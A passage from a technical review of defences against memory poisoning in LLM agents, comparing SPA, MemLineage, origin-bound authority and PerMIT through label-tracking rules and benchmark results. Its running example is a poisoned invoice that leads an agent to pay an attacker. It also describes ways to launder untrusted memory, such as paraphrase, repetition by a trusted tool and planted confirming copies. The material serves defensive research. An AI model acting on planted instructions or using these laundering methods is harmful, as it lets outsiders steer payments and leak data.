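| Monday: agent reads the invoice | Context becomes untrusted | Context becomes untrusted |
| Monday: agent saves the note | Note is untrusted | Note has no label |
| Thursday: agent reads the note | Context becomes untrusted | Context stays trusted |
| Thursday: agent calls `send_money` | Policy refuses the call | Policy allows the call |

In the last column, the harness tracks labels correctly on Monday, but on Thursday it treats the note as the agent's own trusted text. Microsoft's framework and LLMbda would make the same mistake if the storage lost the label, since both treat unlabelled data as trusted. Treating unlabelled data as untrusted would stop the payment, but it would also restrict the agent after it read any harmless note. An auditor such as NeuroTaint might find the link between the two sessions in the logs, but only after the agent had made the payment.

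### How SPA checks the payment

Girrens and Wang designed SPA for agents that handle a series of requests. As in CaMeL, the planner writes a complete program for each request before any tool runs. The programming language has only six kinds of step: retrieve a saved result, call a tool, query a quarantined model, display something, branch, and loop. It has no arithmetic or user-defined functions, so a checker can find every dependency by reading the program.

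The checker examines both sides of each branch before execution. Fenton's example, in which a secret leaks through an assignment that never runs, is impossible in this language because a branch cannot change a variable defined outside it.

When a run succeeds, SPA saves each result in three parts: the value, its label and a description. The planner wrote the description in advance, without seeing the value. On Thursday it reads only the description, "payment details from the Acme invoice", and writes this plan:

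```
details = retrieve("acme_payment_details")
send_money(to=details.account, amount=details.amount)
```

The first step restores Monday's label along with the value. The checker then labels each step by joining the labels of its inputs x₁ to xₙ with the program-counter label, pc, which covers the decisions that led to the step:

```
label of a step  =  pc ⊔ label(x₁) ⊔ ... ⊔ label(xₙ)
```

The program-counter label starts as the label of the user's request. If we treat the invoice as public, the label of the payment step is

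```
(trusted, public) ⊔ (untrusted, public) = (untrusted, public)
```

The policy for `send_money` requires trusted input, so the checker rejects the plan and no step runs.

The rule also covers decisions. Suppose the user types the correct account number and amount on Thursday, but asks the agent to pay only if the saved invoice is marked overdue:

```
if details.overdue:
    send_money(to="1180-2254", amount=2400)
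```

Both arguments are now trusted, but the untrusted condition makes the program-counter label untrusted inside the branch, which also makes the payment step untrusted. The checker rejects this plan too, because whoever wrote the invoice could decide whether the payment goes out.

SPA doesn't let the planner revise a rejected plan, so the checker's verdicts can't leak information through repeated attempts, as they could in CaMeL's retry loop. One implicit flow between sessions apparently remains, because SPA saves results only if the run succeeds, and the next planner can see which results exist. If something in the invoice makes Monday's run fail, Thursday's planner sees a shorter list of results and may write a different plan. Trident would count this as one bit of leakage. Girrens and Wang do not claim to prove noninterference.

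### What the label checks cost

Girrens and Wang tested SPA on AgentDojo and on AgentDojo-MQ, a version in which they split each of the 97 tasks into two to five successive requests. The planner and the quarantined model both ran on GPT-5.4 nano, a small model. The table shows the tasks completed when there was no attack and the share of 949 attacks that succeeded.

| SPA | AgentDojo: tasks completed | AgentDojo: attacks succeeding | AgentDojo-MQ: tasks completed | AgentDojo-MQ: attacks succeeding |
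|---|---|---|---|---|
| Without label checks | 53.0% | 0.4% | 62.5% | 0.3% |
| With label checks | 29.0% | 0.0% | 35.3% | 0.2% |

The last figure represents two runs, and in both the checker had already rejected the plan, so they were probably scoring errors.

The checks reduced the number of completed tasks by nearly half. On the original AgentDojo, the checker rejected about 53% of the plans, usually because they passed an untrusted result to a tool that required trusted input. SPA has no endorsement, so it would reject Thursday's payment even if the invoice were genuine. Girrens and Wang don't report running time or token use, although SPA needs only one call to the planner per request.

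The attack figures provide little evidence about memory, so the rule itself is the better argument for SPA's handling of stored data. Planning before reading stopped almost every attack even without label checks, and the injected instructions were not designed to take effect on a later request. Even when Girrens and Wang let the planner read the saved values, which exposes it to stored injections, only 0.6% of attacks succeeded.

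The planner could usually find saved results even though their values were hidden. With label checks on, it retrieved the right result in 89.9% of the cases where an earlier request had saved one. Including the cases where the result was missing, the figure is 73.4%.

### When the agent rewrites what it has read

SPA can compute a label for every saved result because each one comes from a step in a checked plan. Many agents instead write notes in their own words whenever they choose. A digital signature on such a note proves that the agent wrote it, but not where the agent got the information.

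*Memlineage* (Ouyang and Hou, 2026) adds to the signature a record of what each note was derived from. The system links each new note to the stored entries that were in the context when the agent wrote it, and gives each link a weight between 0 and 1 for how much the entry influenced the note. The note takes the least trusted label among the entries whose weight exceeds a threshold. Ouyang and Hou prove that an untrusted label survives any chain of rewriting as long as every link's weight exceeds the threshold.

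If no link does, MemLineage treats the note as trusted. In one test setting, the weights fall with each rewriting: 0.9, 0.63, 0.44, 0.31, 0.22. With a threshold of 0.3, the label lasts through four rewritings and is lost at the fifth.

The main tests avoided this problem by giving every retrieved entry a weight of 1, which has the same effect as labelling a response with its whole context. In a two-session test, the agent summarised an outsider's document and later used only the summary. With signatures alone, the summary counted as trusted and the agent sent the email the attacker wanted. MemLineage kept the link to the document and blocked the email. With GPT-5.3-Codex as the agent's model, the undefended agent sent the email in 5 of 20 trials (25%) and the protected agent in none, although the 95% confidence interval for the protected agent's rate extends to 16%. Each of MemLineage's own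 operations took less than a millisecond. Estimating finer weights with a second language model would add a model call for every note.

Ouyang and Hou state that FIDES does not keep labels when an agent writes to memory. However, the published FIDES algorithm labels any stored data that a tool may have changed, so the labels would be lost only if the harness did not save them.

*Securing LLM-Agent Long-Term Memory Against Poisoning* (Louck, 2026) uses a model checker, a program that explores every state a small system can reach, to find which checks an attacker can defeat. The checker found an attack in which the agent stores untrusted text, paraphrases it and acts on the paraphrase. The paraphrase looks harmless and has lost its link to the source, so the attack defeats any check that relies on the wording or the link. An attacker can also have a trusted tool repeat the text, or plant several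 copies that appear to confirm one another.

Louck's remedy is origin-bound authority. The harness records the source of each text when it arrives, and everything derived from an untrusted source stays untrusted, however the agent rewords it. If the agent passes untrusted text to a trusted tool, the result is also untrusted. The model checker found no violations in the 3,270 reachable states of a system with three memory items and up to two sessions. An additional argument, made partly by hand, extends the result to larger systems. The guarantee depends on the harness identifying every source correctly.

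Unlike SPA, this design provides a way to use untrusted values. The agent may pay the account in Monday's note if two independent trusted sources, such as the company's supplier register and the bank, confirm the number. Otherwise the user can authorise that exact payment once. Without confirmation by trusted sources, the share of tasks completed fell from 96% to 77%.

In tests with eight models, the three ways of disguising a source succeeded 68% of the time against an undefended agent. All 192 attempts of each kind failed against origin-bound authority, which took about a microsecond per decision. A stand-in for CaMeL and FIDES that treated everything in memory as trusted also let 68% through. Jiang, Bai and colleagues (2026) point out in *PerMIT* that the stand-in's result applies only to that configuration.

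### Noninterference that allows for recorded releases

If a user approves the account number from Monday's invoice, the invoice influences the payment, so full noninterference no longer holds. Jiang and colleagues prove a weaker property for PerMIT, their memory system.

PerMIT's protected model plans and calls tools, but receives only a handle for any text from outside. Before the harness passes such text to a tool, it shows the exact value to a reviewer, who can be the user or another language model. It records everything it displays and every decision the reviewer makes. Take two runs with the same typed requests, trusted memory, random choices and timetable of events, but with any differences in their untrusted text. Then

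```
record(run₁) = record(run₂)   ⇒   actions(run₁) = actions(run₂)
```

where the actions include the protected model's tool calls and its use of memory.

Suppose the stored invoice in one run contains a hidden instruction to email out the customer list, and the invoice in the other run does not. On Thursday, the harness displays the same account number in both runs, and the user accepts it. If everything else displayed is also the same, the records are equal, so the agent makes the same calls and the hidden instruction has no effect. If the invoices contain different account numbers, the records differ and the theorem allows different payments. Untrusted text can therefore change the agent's actions only if it changes something in the record.

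This holds only if the handles reveal nothing about the text behind them. In FIDES, the planning model could count hidden messages and base a decision on their number. PerMIT names its handles according to the protected model's own operations, and a search that finds nothing returns the same kind of handle as a successful one.

Trident's proof holds the user's decisions fixed and leaves out what led to them. PerMIT's record also contains what the reviewer saw, so an investigator can trace a bad payment to the display that preceded it. Neither theorem guarantees that the decision was right. Jiang and colleagues used Lean to check the proof for a single user. The proof does not cover timing or whether a run finishes, and it assumes that the harness follows the model used in the proof.

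PerMIT was tested on Trojan Hippo, a benchmark in which an attacker plants text in one session and the agent acts on it in a later one. When the reviewer accepted every request, between 0% and 10% of attacks succeeded, depending on the model. With language models as reviewers, no attacks succeeded, but across a wider set of models these reviewers rejected 3% to 34% of harmless requests. The experiments did not include human reviewers.

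Approvals also carry over to later sessions. Once a user has accepted an account number for `send_money`, the agent can reuse it with that tool without asking, whatever the date, the purpose or the other arguments. If the user accepts the forged number on Thursday, the agent could pay the attacker again a month later, using any amount the user has typed or approved for payments. Louck's one-time authorisation would require a new decision.

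PerMIT can also share approvals between users. When enough people have accepted a stored entry for a tool, others can use it without reviewing it. In a simulated community of 120 users, this reduced the approvals each user had to give by 38%. The risk of spreading a poisoned entry depended mainly on how often honest reviewers recognised it, and requiring more approvals helped only up to a point. The risk also rose when reviewers tended to make the same mistakes, as they might if many users relied on the same language model.
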